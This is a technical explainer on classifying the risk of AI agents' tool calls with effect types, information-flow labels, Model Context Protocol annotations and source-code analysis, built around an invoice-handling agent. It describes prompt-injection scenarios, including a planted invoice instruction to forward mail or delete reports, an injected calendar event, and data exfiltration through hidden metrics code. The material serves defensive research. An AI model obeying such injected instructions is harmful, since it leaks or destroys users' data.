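# Classifying the risk of AI agents' tool calls with effect types and information-flow control

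## What a tool call does, and what program analysis can say about it

An AI agent is a language model connected to tools, so it can read a mailbox, save a file or send a message as well as produce text. Each of these actions begins as a tool call, a structured request from the model that ordinary software carries out. Each call first goes through a program called a gate, which can let it run unattended, confine it in a sandbox (a runtime barrier that limits which files, hosts or processes code can reach), refer it to a person, or refuse it.

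Classifying the risk of a tool call gives the gate a basis for that choice. Programming-language research offers two kinds of evidence. Effect systems determine what a piece of code may access or change, and information-flow control determines which data may reach the code or influence what it does. Both are decades older than language models and were designed for programs that someone could read in full, which is often not possible with an agent's tools.

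### From the model to the tool server

The model only emits a structured request, as Anthropic's *How tool use works* explains, and other code runs the operation and puts the result back into the conversation. The host is the application that runs the model and forwards its requests. The tool server is the program that carries them out, and it may sit on the same machine or on someone else's.

*Towards Practically-Secure Tools for AI Agents* (Adam, Lu and colleagues, 2026) describes the loop. A user types a prompt into the host, and the model reads it and produces a request, usually in JSON (a text format for structured data) or as a short program. An interpreter inside the host, itself an ordinary deterministic program, contacts the tool server. The host then appends the server's answer to the model's input and runs the model again, repeating until the model replies to the user. The interpreter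 is the natural place for a gate because every call passes through it.

Many hosts, such as Anthropic's coding agent Claude Code, connect to one or more servers through an open standard called the Model Context Protocol (MCP). According to the Model Context Protocol's *Tools* (2026), the host first sends a `tools/list` message. The server replies with a definition of each tool: its name, a description in ordinary language, and a schema that lists the arguments and their types. A definition may also include annotations about the tool's behaviour, which the host must treat as untrusted unless it trusts the server. To use a tool, the host sends `tools/call` with the tool's name and arguments, such as `get_weather` and "New York".

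A gate that works from this message alone has little information about the call. Since the July 2026 version of the Model Context Protocol (2026), remote calls have carried the tool's name in an HTTP header, so that a gateway can authorise a call without reading its body. But the name doesn't establish what the tool does, and it may not be unique, since two servers can each offer a tool called `search`.

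Argument types add only limited information about what a call does. One of the standard's examples is a tool named `execute_sql`, which takes a region and a database query, both as text. A query that counts the rows of a table has the same type as one that deletes the table. Another example is a shopping basket that the server identifies by a string such as `bsk_a1b2c3`. Only the server can match that string to a basket and its contents.

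That leaves the tool's description, which can be incomplete or inaccurate, like any documentation. Adam and colleagues describe a `write_file` tool whose description reads, in full, "Writes `content` to file at `path`". The code writes the file, but it also sends the tool's name and the size of the content to a metrics service, which may count as a leak for a company with a closed-source codebase.

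### An agent that handles invoices

Suppose an accounts department asks an agent to read the supplier invoices in an inbox, save a summary in a reports folder, and email the summary to the finance manager. The agent has five tools.

| Tool | Arguments | Purpose |
|---|---|---|
| `read_inbox` | folder: text | fetch messages from a mail folder |
| `write_file` | path: text, content: text | save a file |
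| `send_email` | to: text, body: text | send a message |
| `run_shell` | command: text | run a command on the host's machine |
| `lookup_vat` | number: text | ask a remote service about a supplier's VAT (value-added tax) number |

Every argument is text, so a type checker would accept `write_file` with the path `reports/march.txt` or with `.bashrc`, a file of commands that run whenever the user opens a shell. The argument to `run_shell` is a program. `lookup_vat` is an opaque service, so the department cannot read its code and knows its effects only from what its operator declares or someone observes.

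The inbox also exposes the agent to prompt injection, in which text the agent reads steers it towards actions its user did not ask for. A supplier, or someone posing as one, could include an instruction in an invoice to forward the whole folder to an outside address.

### Effects and effect types

An effect is anything a computation does besides returning a value, such as reading a file, writing to the network or deleting a record. An ordinary type describes only the returned value. Tate and Leijen (2010) observe that most programming languages let programmers use side effects freely, and propose showing a function's potential effects in its type signature. The part of the type that lists these effects is called the effect type.

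The idea is older than that proposal. *Polymorphic Effect Systems* (Lucassen and Gifford, 1988) developed it for parallel computers, where a compiler must determine which expressions can safely run at the same time. Two expressions can interfere if one may write to memory that the other may read or write, and a list of their effects shows whether that can happen. The paper's system describes a program with types, effects and regions, where a region is the area of memory in which an effect may occur. Lucassen's doctoral thesis, *Types and Effects* (1987), gives the rules at length.

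The central statement of such a system is a typing judgement:

```
Γ ⊢ e : T ! E
```

In words: given the assumptions Γ about the types of its variables, the expression e has type T, and evaluating it may cause the effects in the set E and no others. A constant or a variable has the empty set. Defining a function also causes nothing, because the body does not run yet. The body's effects wait in the function's type as its latent effects, written here above the arrow's shaft as `T1 –E→ T2`, and they come due when something calls the function:

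```
if    Γ ⊢ f : (T1 –E→ T2) ! E1
and   Γ ⊢ a : T1 ! E2
then  Γ ⊢ f(a) : T2 ! E1 ∪ E2 ∪ E
```

So a call may have the effects of evaluating the function expression (E1), the effects of evaluating the argument (E2), and the function's latent effects (E). The effect set of a sequence of statements is the union of the statements' sets, so a caller's set includes the sets of everything it calls, however deep the chain of calls goes.

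Here is a cut-down version of the invoice job as a function with a three-line body, leaving out the summarising:

```
def forward_invoices():
    text = read_inbox("invoices")
    write_file("reports/march.txt", text)
    send_email(FINANCE_MANAGER, text)
```

Suppose the latent effects of the three tools are {mail.read}, {file.write} and {mail.send}. The arguments are all constants or variables and contribute nothing. Each line therefore has just the latent effect of its tool, and the body has the union:

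```
∅ ∪ {mail.read} ∪ {file.write} ∪ {mail.send}
  = {mail.read, file.write, mail.send}
```

If we replace `write_file` with the version that reports metrics, its latent effects become {file.write, net.write}, and the set for `forward_invoices` gains net.write even though that function's code is unchanged. A reviewer who read only its three lines could not detect the new effect.

A set like this is still coarse, because `file.write` covers both the reports folder and the shell's start-up file. Lucassen had the same problem with memory. In Lucassen's thesis, an effect has a sort (allocating, reading or writing) and an extent. A gate's designer would call the extent its scope, meaning the particular files, hosts, accounts or records it reaches. Lucassen first considered using memory addresses for the extent but rejected them, because most programs obtain memory while they run and nobody can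 list the addresses beforehand. Variable names and data types failed for other reasons. Regions worked because the programmer decides which locations belong together and names the group. File paths that a language model makes up as it runs are much like those addresses, and the `reports/` in `file.write(reports/)` works like a region.

### Labels and joins

Even a precise effect set doesn't show what data a call carries. Adam and colleagues describe a user who asks an agent to set up a project by copying a configuration file from another project, and later asks it to publish the project on GitHub, a site for sharing code. The user wanted both actions, but the configuration file contained a private API key, a password for programs, and publishing the project exposed it. The researchers saw this happen with Claude 4.5 Haiku. Similarly, in the invoice example, `send_email` has the effect `mail.send`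 whether the email contains invoice totals or the payroll.

Information-flow control deals with this by attaching labels to data. A label records who may read the data (confidentiality) or how far its origin is trusted (integrity). The mathematics comes from Denning's *A Lattice Model of Secure Information Flow* (1976). Denning starts with a finite set of security classes, a relation A → B that holds when information in class A may flow into class B, and an operation that gives the class of any result computed from A and B together. Denning then shows that, to be consistent, these must form a lattice, in which any two classes A and B have a least upper bound, called their join and written A ⊔ B.

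If a program may copy a to b and then b to c, it should also be allowed to copy a to c directly, so permission has to pass along chains. If a program may store a + b in c, it could set b to zero and store a by itself, so the class of the sum cannot be lower than the class of a. Taking the *least* class that satisfies this for both inputs makes the rule no stricter than necessary.

For agents, Kolluri, Sharma and colleagues (2026), in *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy*, use an ordering of public below secret and another of trusted below untrusted. Combining the two gives four labels, here with "private" for secret and with examples from the accounts department:

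| | Trusted | Untrusted |
|---|---|---|
| **Public** | the company's published address | a VAT record from `lookup_vat` |
| **Private** | the user's own notes on a supplier | a supplier's invoice |

Data may flow to the right or downwards in this table, towards more restriction, and never back. The join takes the more restrictive value in each respect. If the agent combines the user's notes (private, trusted) with the VAT record (public, untrusted), the result is private and untrusted, a label that neither input had:

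```
(private, trusted) ⊔ (public, untrusted) = (private, untrusted)
```

"Untrusted" counts as high because both orderings run from data that may go anywhere to data whose flow needs to be monitored.

Labels can be finer than this. In their experiments, Kolluri and colleagues label a document with the set of people allowed to read it, and the join of two labels is the intersection of the sets. If a text draws on one document that A, B and C may read and another that B, C and D may read, only B and C may read the text.

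### Before the run and during it

An analysis can compute effects and labels either before a program runs, by reading its code (static analysis), or while it runs. For labels, the run-time method is taint tracking, which carries labels along with the data so that a result inherits the labels of the data it was made from. Denning's paper already covers both approaches, and distinguishes objects whose label stays fixed from objects whose label changes with their contents. For example, the reports folder could have a fixed label, while the label of the variable `text` could change.

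Static analysis covers every execution the code allows and can be done once, before any call arrives, but it lacks the actual values. Adam and colleagues point out that a path often arrives as an argument of the call, so an analysis of `write_file` has to assume that the write could go anywhere. If the policy is "only write to the workspace folder", static analysis alone would have to reject the tool, which would also block calls that stay inside the folder.

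At run time, the path is known when the write happens, so a check can compare it with the policy. But the check covers only the current execution, and simple tracking can miss an implicit flow, where the branch a program takes leaks information. Also, if a check fails at the fourth step of a job, the first three steps have already had their effects. Adam and colleagues list this as an open problem for their own design.

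Static and run-time checking can be combined. *Intensional Effect Polymorphism*, by Long, Liu and Rajan, describes an effect system that leaves part of the checking until run time, when more precise information is available. Adam and colleagues use static analysis to find a tool's effects and put small sandboxes around each effect to check its scope.

### Soundness, false alarms and Rice's theorem

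An analysis is sound if, within its stated assumptions, it never misses an effect or flow that can occur. An analysis that reports every possible effect for every program is sound but useless, because it over-approximates, meaning that it reports effects or flows that may never occur. Each such report is a potential false alarm.

Conditionals are the simplest source of overestimation. Suppose a script emails the finance manager when the invoices total more than 10,000 euros and otherwise writes a file. The effect set contains both actions, although no run performs both. Lucassen calls this rule "rather conservative" because it treats the two branches as if both always ran. The thesis mentions a finer rule, in which the effect would depend on the condition's value, but does not pursue it. A worse case for a gate would be a script that calls `run_shell` only when a debugging switch is on. The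 analysis would report that call every time, even if nobody ever turned the switch on.

Better engineering can remove many such alarms but cannot remove them all. Rice's theorem, which the logician Henry Rice published in 1953, concerns properties of what programs do, as opposed to how their text looks. If some programs have such a property and others lack it, no algorithm can decide correctly for every program whether it has the property. For effects there is a direct proof. Take any program P that has no effects of its own, and write:

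```
def f():
    P()
    delete_records()
```

This function deletes records exactly when P finishes. An analysis that was always right about f would determine whether P finishes, for any P, and Alan Turing showed in 1936 that no algorithm can do that. So an analysis that accepts arbitrary programs and always returns an answer must sometimes miss an effect or report one that never happens. For a gate, a false alarm is usually better than a missed effect, because a person can overrule a false alarm but may never hear about a missed deletion.

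The theorem is about *arbitrary* programs, and researchers have long avoided its limits by narrowing the problem. Denning knew of a proof that, in a general model of access control, no algorithm can always tell whether a right to some object will leak, and looked for restrictions that would make security easy to decide. Lucassen asked programmers to declare the effects of their functions at certain points, so that the compiler only had to check the declarations against the rules. The compiler can do this exactly, although the rules themselves are still conservative.

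Adam and colleagues provide suggestive but small evidence of how much false alarms matter in practice. They set up three situations in which a developer works with an agent, each in a harmless and a harmful version, and replayed recorded sessions under different protections. Static analysis alone blocked all three harmful versions, but it also blocked a harmless one, in which the user had asked for a change to `.bashrc`, because it could not establish where the writes would go. Static analysis combined with sandboxes got all six right. The researchers devised the three situations themselves, and the policies were supplied in advance, so the results show that the combination can work but are a poor measure of how often it will.

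In Adam and colleagues' design, the analysis examines a tool server's source code, but the call goes to whatever program is running on the server's machine. The results therefore depend on the assumption that this program matches the source code. To verify that, they would need remote attestation, a hardware-backed proof that the server is running the code they analysed.

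## Choosing the risk classes

A gate can respond to a call in only a few ways, so it needs classes, meaning groups of calls that it can treat alike. The simplest scheme has two classes, reads and writes, and lets the reads through. A finer scheme is better only if the extra distinctions affect what the gate does. Jonathan Hefner, who helps maintain the Model Context Protocol, applied this test to a draft set of new tool annotations: "It's not clear to me exactly how a client would behave differently". (A client here is the part of the host that talks to a tool server.)

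### The protocol's four annotations

Since March 2025 the protocol has had a small vocabulary for risk. A tool's definition may include four true-or-false annotations about its behaviour, which the standard calls hints. The Model Context Protocol schema defines them as follows:

| Hint | Meaning if true | Default |
|---|---|---|
| `readOnlyHint` | the tool does not modify its environment | false |
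| `destructiveHint` | the tool may make destructive changes (if false, it only adds things) | true |
| `idempotentHint` | repeating a call with the same arguments has no additional effect | false |
| `openWorldHint` | the tool may deal with an open-ended set of outside entities | true |

Replacing a file's contents with the word "paid" is idempotent, but adding the line "paid" to the file is not. The destructive and idempotent hints apply only when the tool is not read-only. The schema illustrates the open-world hint with a web search, which is open, and a memory tool, which is closed. The boundary depends on where the server runs. A March 2026 post on the Model Context Protocol blog points out that "external" might mean anything outside a company's network or anything beyond the local machine.

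By default, a client should assume that a tool without annotations modifies its environment, perhaps destructively, is unsafe to call repeatedly, and interacts with external entities. One of the schema's examples, a tool that adds two numbers, has no annotations, so a client that followed these defaults would put it in the same class as `run_shell`.

### What an untrusted hint is worth

The server's author writes the hints, and the protocol doesn't verify them, so a tool marked read-only can still delete files. Under the schema, clients should therefore never base tool-use decisions on annotations from untrusted servers.

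That rule came out of a disagreement during the original review, according to the Model Context Protocol post. Justin Spahr-Summers, one of the protocol's creators, thought the information would be very useful if clients could trust it, but wondered what a client could do with a flag it couldn't trust. Basil Hosmer argued that clients should ignore every annotation from an untrusted server, even the tool's display title. As a compromise, the reviewers called all the annotations hints, required clients to distrust them by default, and let each client choose how far to rely on them, depending on how well it knows the server.

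A client that follows Hosmer's position and ignores hints from unknown servers gives up no safety, because each default is already the most cautious value. The only change a hint can make is to lower the client's assessment of the risk, and a dishonest author would fake the values that lower it. If an unknown server marks a tool as destructive, the client was already assuming that. The client will, however, raise more false alarms if it ignores these hints.

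The hints are more useful when a company runs both the server and the client, but they can still be wrong by mistake. The developer of the `write_file` tool that reports to a metrics service might think of it as a local file tool and mark it as closed-world.

### What servers declare

Trofimov and Novikov (2026), in *When Tool Calls Succeed but Workflows Fail*, measured how servers use the four hints. They took a snapshot of the protocol's official registry on 27 July 2026, which had 59,625 entries for 18,688 distinct servers. They excluded the 9,454 servers that had no remote address, because examining them would have meant running the packages. They sent the other 9,234 an anonymous `tools/list` request and did not call any tools. Of these servers, 4,838 returned at least one tool, for a total of 98,291 tools and a median of 11 per server. Almost all the others failed to connect.

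A single publisher, pipeworx-io, runs 1,274 of the responding servers and supplies 44,227 of the tools, or 45.0%. Every one of its tools has all four hints set, so Trofimov and Novikov also give the results without it:

| Share of tools | All | Without pipeworx-io |
|---|---|---|
| No annotation | 26.0% | 47.2% |
| All four hints set | 61.7% | 30.3% |
| Destructive hint set, but the tool is marked read-only | 52.8% | 26.0% |
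| Destructive hint set, and it applies | 12.9% | 11.7% |
| Marked as destructive | 3.1% | 3.2% |

Only 12.9% of tools have a classification as destructive or not that a gate could use. Although 65.8% of all tools set the destructive hint, most of those are also marked read-only, and the hint has no meaning for a tool that modifies nothing.

The second column is a better guide to what server authors usually do, because one publisher used the same template 1,274 times. That template also accounts for most uses of the most common combination of hints (read-only, non-destructive, idempotent and open-world), whose share falls from 39.9% to 7.3% without that publisher. But the share of tools with an applicable classification as destructive or non-destructive hardly changes, so one large publisher doesn't explain the shortage of usable classifications.

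The census covers only remote servers that responded. It may therefore be least informative about the tools that can do the most local damage, such as `write_file` and `run_shell`, which often run on the user's own machine. It also counts what servers declare without testing whether it is true.

### Six things to record

The hints are a reasonable start, but a gate needs a fuller record for each call: the kind of effect, its scope, whether someone can undo it, whether the agent can safely repeat it, whether it reaches outsiders, and how certain these entries are.

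A single risk score for each call can't capture these properties, because a call can be safer by one and riskier by another. Trofimov and Novikov compare adding one to a counter with deleting a record. Two additions give the same total in either order, but accidentally repeating one makes the total wrong. Deleting a record twice has the same effect as deleting it once, but it matters whether the deletion comes before or after another operation on the record.

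The effect types in the previous section, such as `file.write(reports/)`, give the kind of effect and its scope. The four hints don't include scope. They are also part of the tool's definition, so they are the same for every call, although `write_file` is much riskier with the path `.bashrc` than with `reports/march.txt`. Tool Resolution, a draft proposal for the Model Context Protocol (*SEP-1862*, 2025), would provide annotations for a particular call before it runs. Until something like that exists, the gate has to work out the scope from the arguments.

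Whether someone can undo an effect is separate from whether it is destructive. Moving a file to the trash removes it from its folder, but the user can put it back. Another Model Context Protocol (2026) post, from 13 March, uses this example to explain a possible `reversibleHint`. Sending an email only adds something, so an honest author could mark `send_email` as non-destructive, but nobody can reliably take the message back.

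A yes or no is often too crude to describe whether an effect can be undone. Trofimov and Novikov describe an agent with a travel budget of 1,500 euros that books a 900-euro flight and a 700-euro hotel at the same time. Both bookings succeed, which exceeds the budget. The agent cancels the hotel, but the flight is non-refundable. In another example, a company withdraws an offer after a supplier has already acted on it, and the withdrawal does not reverse what the supplier did. So the record should include the action that would undo the effect and anything that would remain afterwards.

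Whether a call is safe to repeat matters because connections fail. Suppose an agent pays an invoice and gets no confirmation. Trying again makes the company pay twice if the first payment went through, and requesting a refund is an error if it didn't. Some services prevent double payment with an idempotency key, an identifier that lets them recognise a repeated request. The idempotent hint can't supply this key, so the record should show whether a call is safe to repeat without a key, safe only with one, or unsafe.

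A web search may bring in text that an attacker wrote, and an email may send private data to outsiders. The open-world hint covers both risks with one value. The Model Context Protocol post of 13 March describes an `egressHint` that would separate them by marking the tools that can send data out.

The last entry, certainty, records where the others came from. A reviewer may have established an entry from source code, the server's operator may have declared it, someone may have observed it in tests, or it may be a default. Trofimov and Novikov likewise want tool contracts to separate established properties from assumed and unknown ones, because acting on an assumption can itself cause a failure, such as trying to reverse an operation that has no true reverse. Each entry needs its own certainty, since the source code of `write_file` can establish the kind of effect but not its scope.

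### Why risk belongs to combinations

Even a complete record of one call may not show a danger that comes from using several tools together. The programmer Simon Willison uses the term "lethal trifecta" for the combination of access to private data, exposure to untrusted content, and the ability to communicate externally. If an agent has all three, an attacker who controls one piece of the untrusted content can use prompt injection to get the agent to read private data and send it out.

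The Model Context Protocol post cites a demonstration in which researchers put malicious instructions in the description of a Google Calendar event. The agent received the instructions through a calendar server and could carry them out with a separate tool for running code on the local machine. Users often combine tools from several servers in one session, so a server's author can't know which other tools the agent will have.

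The invoice agent meets all three conditions with two tools. `read_inbox` gives it private data and text from outsiders, and `send_email` gives it a way out. Removing `send_email` would not be enough, because `lookup_vat` also sends text to an outside company:

| Tool | Private data | Untrusted content | A way out |
|---|---|---|---|
| `read_inbox` | yes | yes | no |
| `write_file` | no | no | only if others can read the file |
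| `send_email` | no | no | yes |
| `run_shell` | yes | yes | yes |
| `lookup_vat` | no | yes | yes |

With internet access, `run_shell` meets all three conditions alone, since a command can read local files, download a web page and upload data. For the other tools, the gate has to take the union of the columns over every tool in the session. This coarse test can show that theft is possible, but not whether private data has reached an outgoing message. It also covers only theft. An attacker could plant an instruction in an invoice to delete the reports folder, which requires neither private data nor a way to send it out, so the gate still needs the entry on whether an action can be undone.

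To narrow the test, a host would have to know which data is private or untrusted as well as which tools are available. The discussion of Tool Resolution on the Model Context Protocol site describes SEP-1913, a proposal by Sam Morrow of GitHub and Robert Reichel of OpenAI that would let servers name the source of their results and mark them as sensitive, private, from the open world or possibly malicious. Under the rules outlined in the Model Context Protocol post of 13 March, sensitivity could rise but never fall within a session, a true-or-false mark would stay on if any input had it, and the list of sources would grow. These rules work like Denning's join. The marks would still come from the server, so the dispute over untrusted hints would apply to them too.

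SEP-1913 is not part of the Model Context Protocol standard. The protocol's *Tool Annotations Charter* (April 2026) lists it as a draft, along with Tool Resolution and two other proposals. The protocol's *Key Changes* (2026) for the July specification includes no new tool annotation, and in late November the protocol's index of proposals listed none as accepted or final.

A change to the tool annotations does not look close. The Model Context Protocol (2026) roadmap, updated on 16 November, does not include them in any priority area, and proposals outside those areas face a longer queue and a higher bar. The next specification is due on 30 March 2027, and its review window closes two and a half months before that. An older proposal also needs a working group or the core maintainers to sponsor it before its next formal review. The group that discusses tool annotations is an interest group,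 which can only make recommendations.

Some developers have started labelling tool outputs without the standard. GitHub's tool server has a package, documented on pkg.go.dev, that defines confidentiality and integrity labels for these outputs. The label for a file's contents depends on whether they are private. A separate service enforces the labels.

### The invoice tools, classified

Suppose the accounts department has read the source code of every tool except `lookup_vat` and found that each does what its description says. The record for each tool, before a particular call arrives, would look like this:

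| | `read_inbox` | `write_file` | `send_email` | `run_shell` | `lookup_vat` |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| **Kind of effect** | reads mail | creates or overwrites a file | sends a message | whatever the command does | sends a query and returns a record |
| **Scope** | one mail folder | any path, until the call names one | any address, until the call names one | all that the host's account can reach | the operator's service, and perhaps others |
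| **Undo** | nothing to undo | only with a backup | no | assume not | no, the query has left |
| **Safe to repeat** | yes | yes, with the same content | no, it sends a second copy | assume not | probably, but there may be a fee |
| **Outsiders** | their text comes in | none, unless they can read the file | data may go out | both directions | both directions |
| **Certainty** | high | high for the kind, low for the scope | high for the kind, low for the scope | low until someone examines the command | low, only the operator's declaration |
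| **Read/write scheme** | read | write | write | write | read |

A read/write scheme makes its worst errors on the two reads, because it would let both run unattended. `read_inbox` changes nothing, but it supplies the private data and possibly the attacker's instructions. `lookup_vat` takes free text as its argument, so a planted instruction could have the agent put a supplier's bank details where the VAT number should go. An honest operator might well mark `lookup_vat` read-only, non-destructive, idempotent and open-world, the most common combination in the census. A gate could use the open-world hint to detect that outsiders were involved, but not that data was leaving.

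The scheme classes both `write_file` and `send_email` as writes, which is correct but too broad. The class covers saving a new summary in the reports folder, overwriting `.bashrc` and emailing the payroll to a stranger. If the gate refers every write to a person, that person has to approve even the routine summary, but if it allows every write, the two dangerous calls go through.

Classifying `run_shell` as "write" is the cautious choice, but it raises a false alarm whenever the command only lists a folder. Classifying each command as a read or a write would remove that false alarm but create a worse problem, because a command that uploads the reports folder to an outside server changes no files on the machine and could therefore count as a read.

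## Inferring a tool's effects from its source code

The classification of the invoice tools assumed that someone had read the source code of four of them. This is slow and must be repeated for each new version of a tool, but a program can do much of it. The program finds the function that handles the tool's calls (the handler), follows every function call from there, and identifies library functions with known effects. It then attributes those effects to the handler, and can also record which of the tool's arguments reach which effect.

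### Finding the entry point

The entry point is the function that runs when a call for the tool arrives. In the simplest servers, the developer marks it with a line such as `@tool`, and the analysis only has to search for that line. In *Unsafe by Flow*, Hou, Zhao and Wang (2026) examined 100 Python servers and 100 JavaScript or TypeScript servers by hand. Only 54 of the Python servers and 30 of the JavaScript or TypeScript servers declared their tools directly. Another 13 Python servers and 44 JavaScript or TypeScript servers had a general function that receives every `tools/call` message and uses the tool's name to choose what to run. An analysis that started at that function without separating its branches would assign each tool the effects of every tool on the server.

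Hou and colleagues' analyser, MCP-BiFlow, finds where a server publishes a tool's name and where it selects the code for that name, then starts its analysis from that tool's branch. When they turned this step off, the number of confirmed findings in a set they had reviewed fell from 424 to 287.

Source-code analysis will still miss some tools. *Give Them an Inch and They Will Take a Mile* (2026) describes a search for entry points that uses CodeQL, GitHub's code analyser. In 100 sampled projects, the search found every JavaScript and TypeScript tool but only 94.08% of the Python ones. A gate can detect missed tools by comparing its effect records with the server's reply to `tools/list`, which lists the tools the server offers. It can then apply the most cautious defaults to any tool without a record.

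### From library calls to an effect set

The next step is to build a call graph, in which each function is a point and each call is an arrow from the caller to the function it calls. Any function that can be reached by following the arrows from the entry point might run.

It isn't always obvious where an arrow in the call graph should go, because an expression such as `x.to_string()` runs different code depending on the type of `x`. *Paralegal* (Adam, Zech and colleagues, 2025) analyses Rust partly because which code a call will run is usually fixed before a Rust program starts. In dynamic languages, this is often determined only at run time, which makes a complete call graph much harder to build.

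The analysis also needs a list of library functions and their effects. Adam and colleagues argue for marking fairly high-level functions. The operating system's `write` operation is too general because it can write to a file, a network connection or another process, whereas Python's `HTTPConnection.request` only produces network traffic. Most tools rely on a few popular libraries, so the list can be short. If a tool bypasses those libraries and calls the operating system directly, the analysis should reject the call or record a very broad effect.

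Capslock, which began at Google, applies this method to Go packages, and has a Java version and an experimental Rust version. Capslock's *Know what your dependencies can do* shows the output for a project that uses a database and the version-control program git. The output lists access to files and the network, and the ability to run other programs, which comes from a library that sometimes has to start git. Two further categories, `REFLECT` and `UNANALYZED`, mark code whose behaviour the call graph may not capture. A gate should treat code in either category as having unknown effects, not as having none.

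Once the library calls have their marks, the effects travel back along the arrows. For a function f that calls the functions g1 to gn:

```
E(f) = D(f) ∪ E(g1) ∪ ... ∪ E(gn)
```

E(f) is the full effect set of f, and D(f) contains the effects of the marked library functions that f calls directly. This is the same union as in the typing rules for effects, but here nobody has to declare anything. If two functions call each other, their effect sets depend on each other, so the analysis starts with empty sets and reapplies the equation until nothing changes. It always finishes because the sets can only grow and the list of possible effects is finite.

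### Which inputs reach which effects

An effect set doesn't show how much control the caller has over what a tool does. A tool that always runs the same harmless command has the same effect set as one that runs whatever text it receives. This difference matters in practice. In *Mitigating Taint-Style Vulnerabilities in MCP Servers via Security-Aware Tool Descriptions*, Shi, Fu and colleagues (2026) studied 53 vulnerabilities in tool servers and found that untrusted input reached a sensitive operation in 81.13% of them.

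To find such paths, MCP-BiFlow marks the tool's arguments and follows them through the code as they are assigned to variables, stored in fields, passed to functions or returned from them. When a marked value reaches a sensitive library call, the route it took is a candidate path. MCP-BiFlow also works backwards from the value the tool returns, to see whether it contains text from a web page, a file or another outside source. A gate can use this backward search to fill in part of the entry on outsiders, because it shows that a tool can bring their text to the model.

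One server that Hou and colleagues examined has a tool for viewing and editing files. When given a folder's path, the tool puts the path in a shell command and runs the command. The tool's name and purpose suggest file access, but its effect set also includes running a program, and the caller's text flows into the command.

Of 32 published vulnerabilities, MCP-BiFlow found 30, Snyk Code ten, Semgrep eight and CodeQL one. CodeQL's low score probably reflects its default rules more than its engine, since *Give Them an Inch and They Will Take a Mile* located many tools using CodeQL with suitable rules. MCP-BiFlow's two misses were both in JavaScript. One involved arguments that the code unpacked into parameters with default values, and the other involved a function passed into a loop.

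The test contained only vulnerable code, so it couldn't measure false alarms. In a separate run over 15,452 repositories, MCP-BiFlow produced 549 groups of suspicious paths, and reviewers confirmed 118 paths in 87 servers. In the first round, the most common reason for rejection was that the caller did not really control where a request went (122 cases). The reviewers kept only problems serious enough to report to developers, so some rejected paths may still be flows that a gate should record.

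### The Brown prototype

Adam and colleagues at Brown University built a prototype that uses an effect analysis to decide on tool calls. It covers servers written in Rust and runs on Paralegal, which some of the same people had developed to find privacy bugs. They tried the prototype on an existing server for software developers. They added the metrics code in the server's `write_file` tool themselves, modelling it on a leak in the agent software OpenClaw.

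Starting from `write_file`, the analysis reaches two marked functions in Rust's standard library. One writes files, and the tool calls it directly. The other writes to a network connection, and the tool reaches it through the metrics module. The resulting summary, which Adam and colleagues call a synopsis, pairs each input with the effects it can reach:

```
path     →  file.write
content  →  file.write
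content  →  net.write
```

The last line shows the effect that the tool's description omits. `content` appears there because the metrics message includes its length. The synopsis would look the same if the tool uploaded the entire file, so it overstates this leak.

The server sends the synopsis to the host when it connects, and before each call the host compares it with a policy. The example policy for file editing has four rules, with later ones overriding earlier ones:

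| When | Rule |
|---|---|
| always | refuse every effect |
| always | allow `net.write` |
| the user wants files edited | allow `file.write` inside `~/workspace` |
| the session involves sensitive data | refuse `net.write` |

If the user is working on proprietary code, the fourth rule forbids network writes, and the host refuses the call because the synopsis lists one. In an ordinary session the network write is acceptable, but the host must still refuse the call because it can't establish that the file write will stay inside the workspace.

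The source code shows whether a tool uses the network, but not where it writes, because `path` is only set when the tool is called. The same line of code can write to a test file in the workspace or to the start-up file `.bashrc`.

The host could inspect the `path` argument before forwarding the call, but the tool might not write to exactly that path. The synopsis establishes only that `path` influences the write. The code might, for example, put a folder name in front of the argument or replace part of it.

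### Sandboxes inside the tool

Adam and colleagues therefore put the check inside the tool, where it runs when the tool writes a file. The developer replaces the ordinary file-writing function with a version from a sandbox library. This version takes one more argument, a configuration that lists the permitted paths, and fails if the actual path isn't among them. For each call, the host creates a configuration from the policy and sends it with the other arguments. Users with different policies can then share a server, which a single sandbox around the whole server would not allow.

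Shell commands need more extensive controls. The prototype keeps a command's file changes temporary until the command ends, then checks them against the policy. It also sends the command's network traffic through a local proxy that permits only certain domains.

The host can't assume that the developer did this correctly. A developer might forget a sandbox or replace the host's configuration with a permissive one. So the prototype analyzes the program a second time to check that every effect happens inside a sandbox and that no instruction can change the host's configuration before it reaches the sandbox. The analysis treats a sandboxed write and a plain write as different effects, and the host rejects a tool with any plain effect that the policy doesn't explicitly allow. If the developer sandboxes the file write but leaves the metrics call unsandboxed, the tool becomes usable in ordinary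 sessions but stays blocked in sensitive ones.

Some tools don't need sandboxes. For example, the same server's "workflow" tool only generates a plan and has no outside effects, so the host can allow it under any policy.

The reliability of the two passes depends on the graph they run on. According to Adam, Zech and colleagues, Paralegal's graph contains every true dependency as long as the program avoids Rust's unsafe features, such as pointer arithmetic and calls to code in other languages. When a library's source is missing, Paralegal estimates its behaviour from the types of its functions. Rust's types show which data a function may change but not whether it opens a network connection, so a gate's designer would have to mark the functions that do by hand or assume that any function with missing source might.

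### Three scenarios, four protections

Adam and colleagues compared their design with three alternatives: no protection, Anthropic's sandbox around the entire server with a single fixed policy, and the static analysis without sandboxes, where the host decides from the synopsis alone.

In the first scenario, a developer asks the agent to test a network connection, save an API key in the project folder and add instructions to `.bashrc`. In the harmful variant, the model guesses the wrong folder for the key. In the second scenario, a developer uses the same tool server for an open-source library and a proprietary application, and the harmful variant uses the server with hidden metrics. In the third, the agent later publishes the copied configuration file on GitHub. The file contains an API key in the harmful variant and a harmless debugging setting in the intended one.

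| Scenario | Variant | No protection | Sandbox around the server | Static analysis alone | Static analysis with inner sandboxes |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Saving a key | intended | allowed | **blocked** | **blocked** | allowed |
| Saving a key | harmful | **allowed** | blocked | blocked | blocked |
| Proprietary code | intended | allowed | allowed | allowed | allowed |
| Proprietary code | harmful | **allowed** | **allowed** | blocked | blocked |
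| Publishing a project | intended | allowed | allowed | allowed | allowed |
| Publishing a project | harmful | **allowed** | **allowed** | blocked | blocked |

Bold marks a wrong result. The sandbox around the server got three of the six cases right, the same number as no protection. Its fixed policy forbids changes to files like `.bashrc`, even when the user requests them, and it cannot detect when a session involves proprietary code or a secret key.

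Static analysis alone got five out of six right, and its one mistake was blocking the intended writes in the first scenario. This score probably overstates its accuracy. In the publishing scenario, it blocked every shell command once the session contained the key, including commands unrelated to publishing. The table doesn't count this as an error because the intended variant contains no key.

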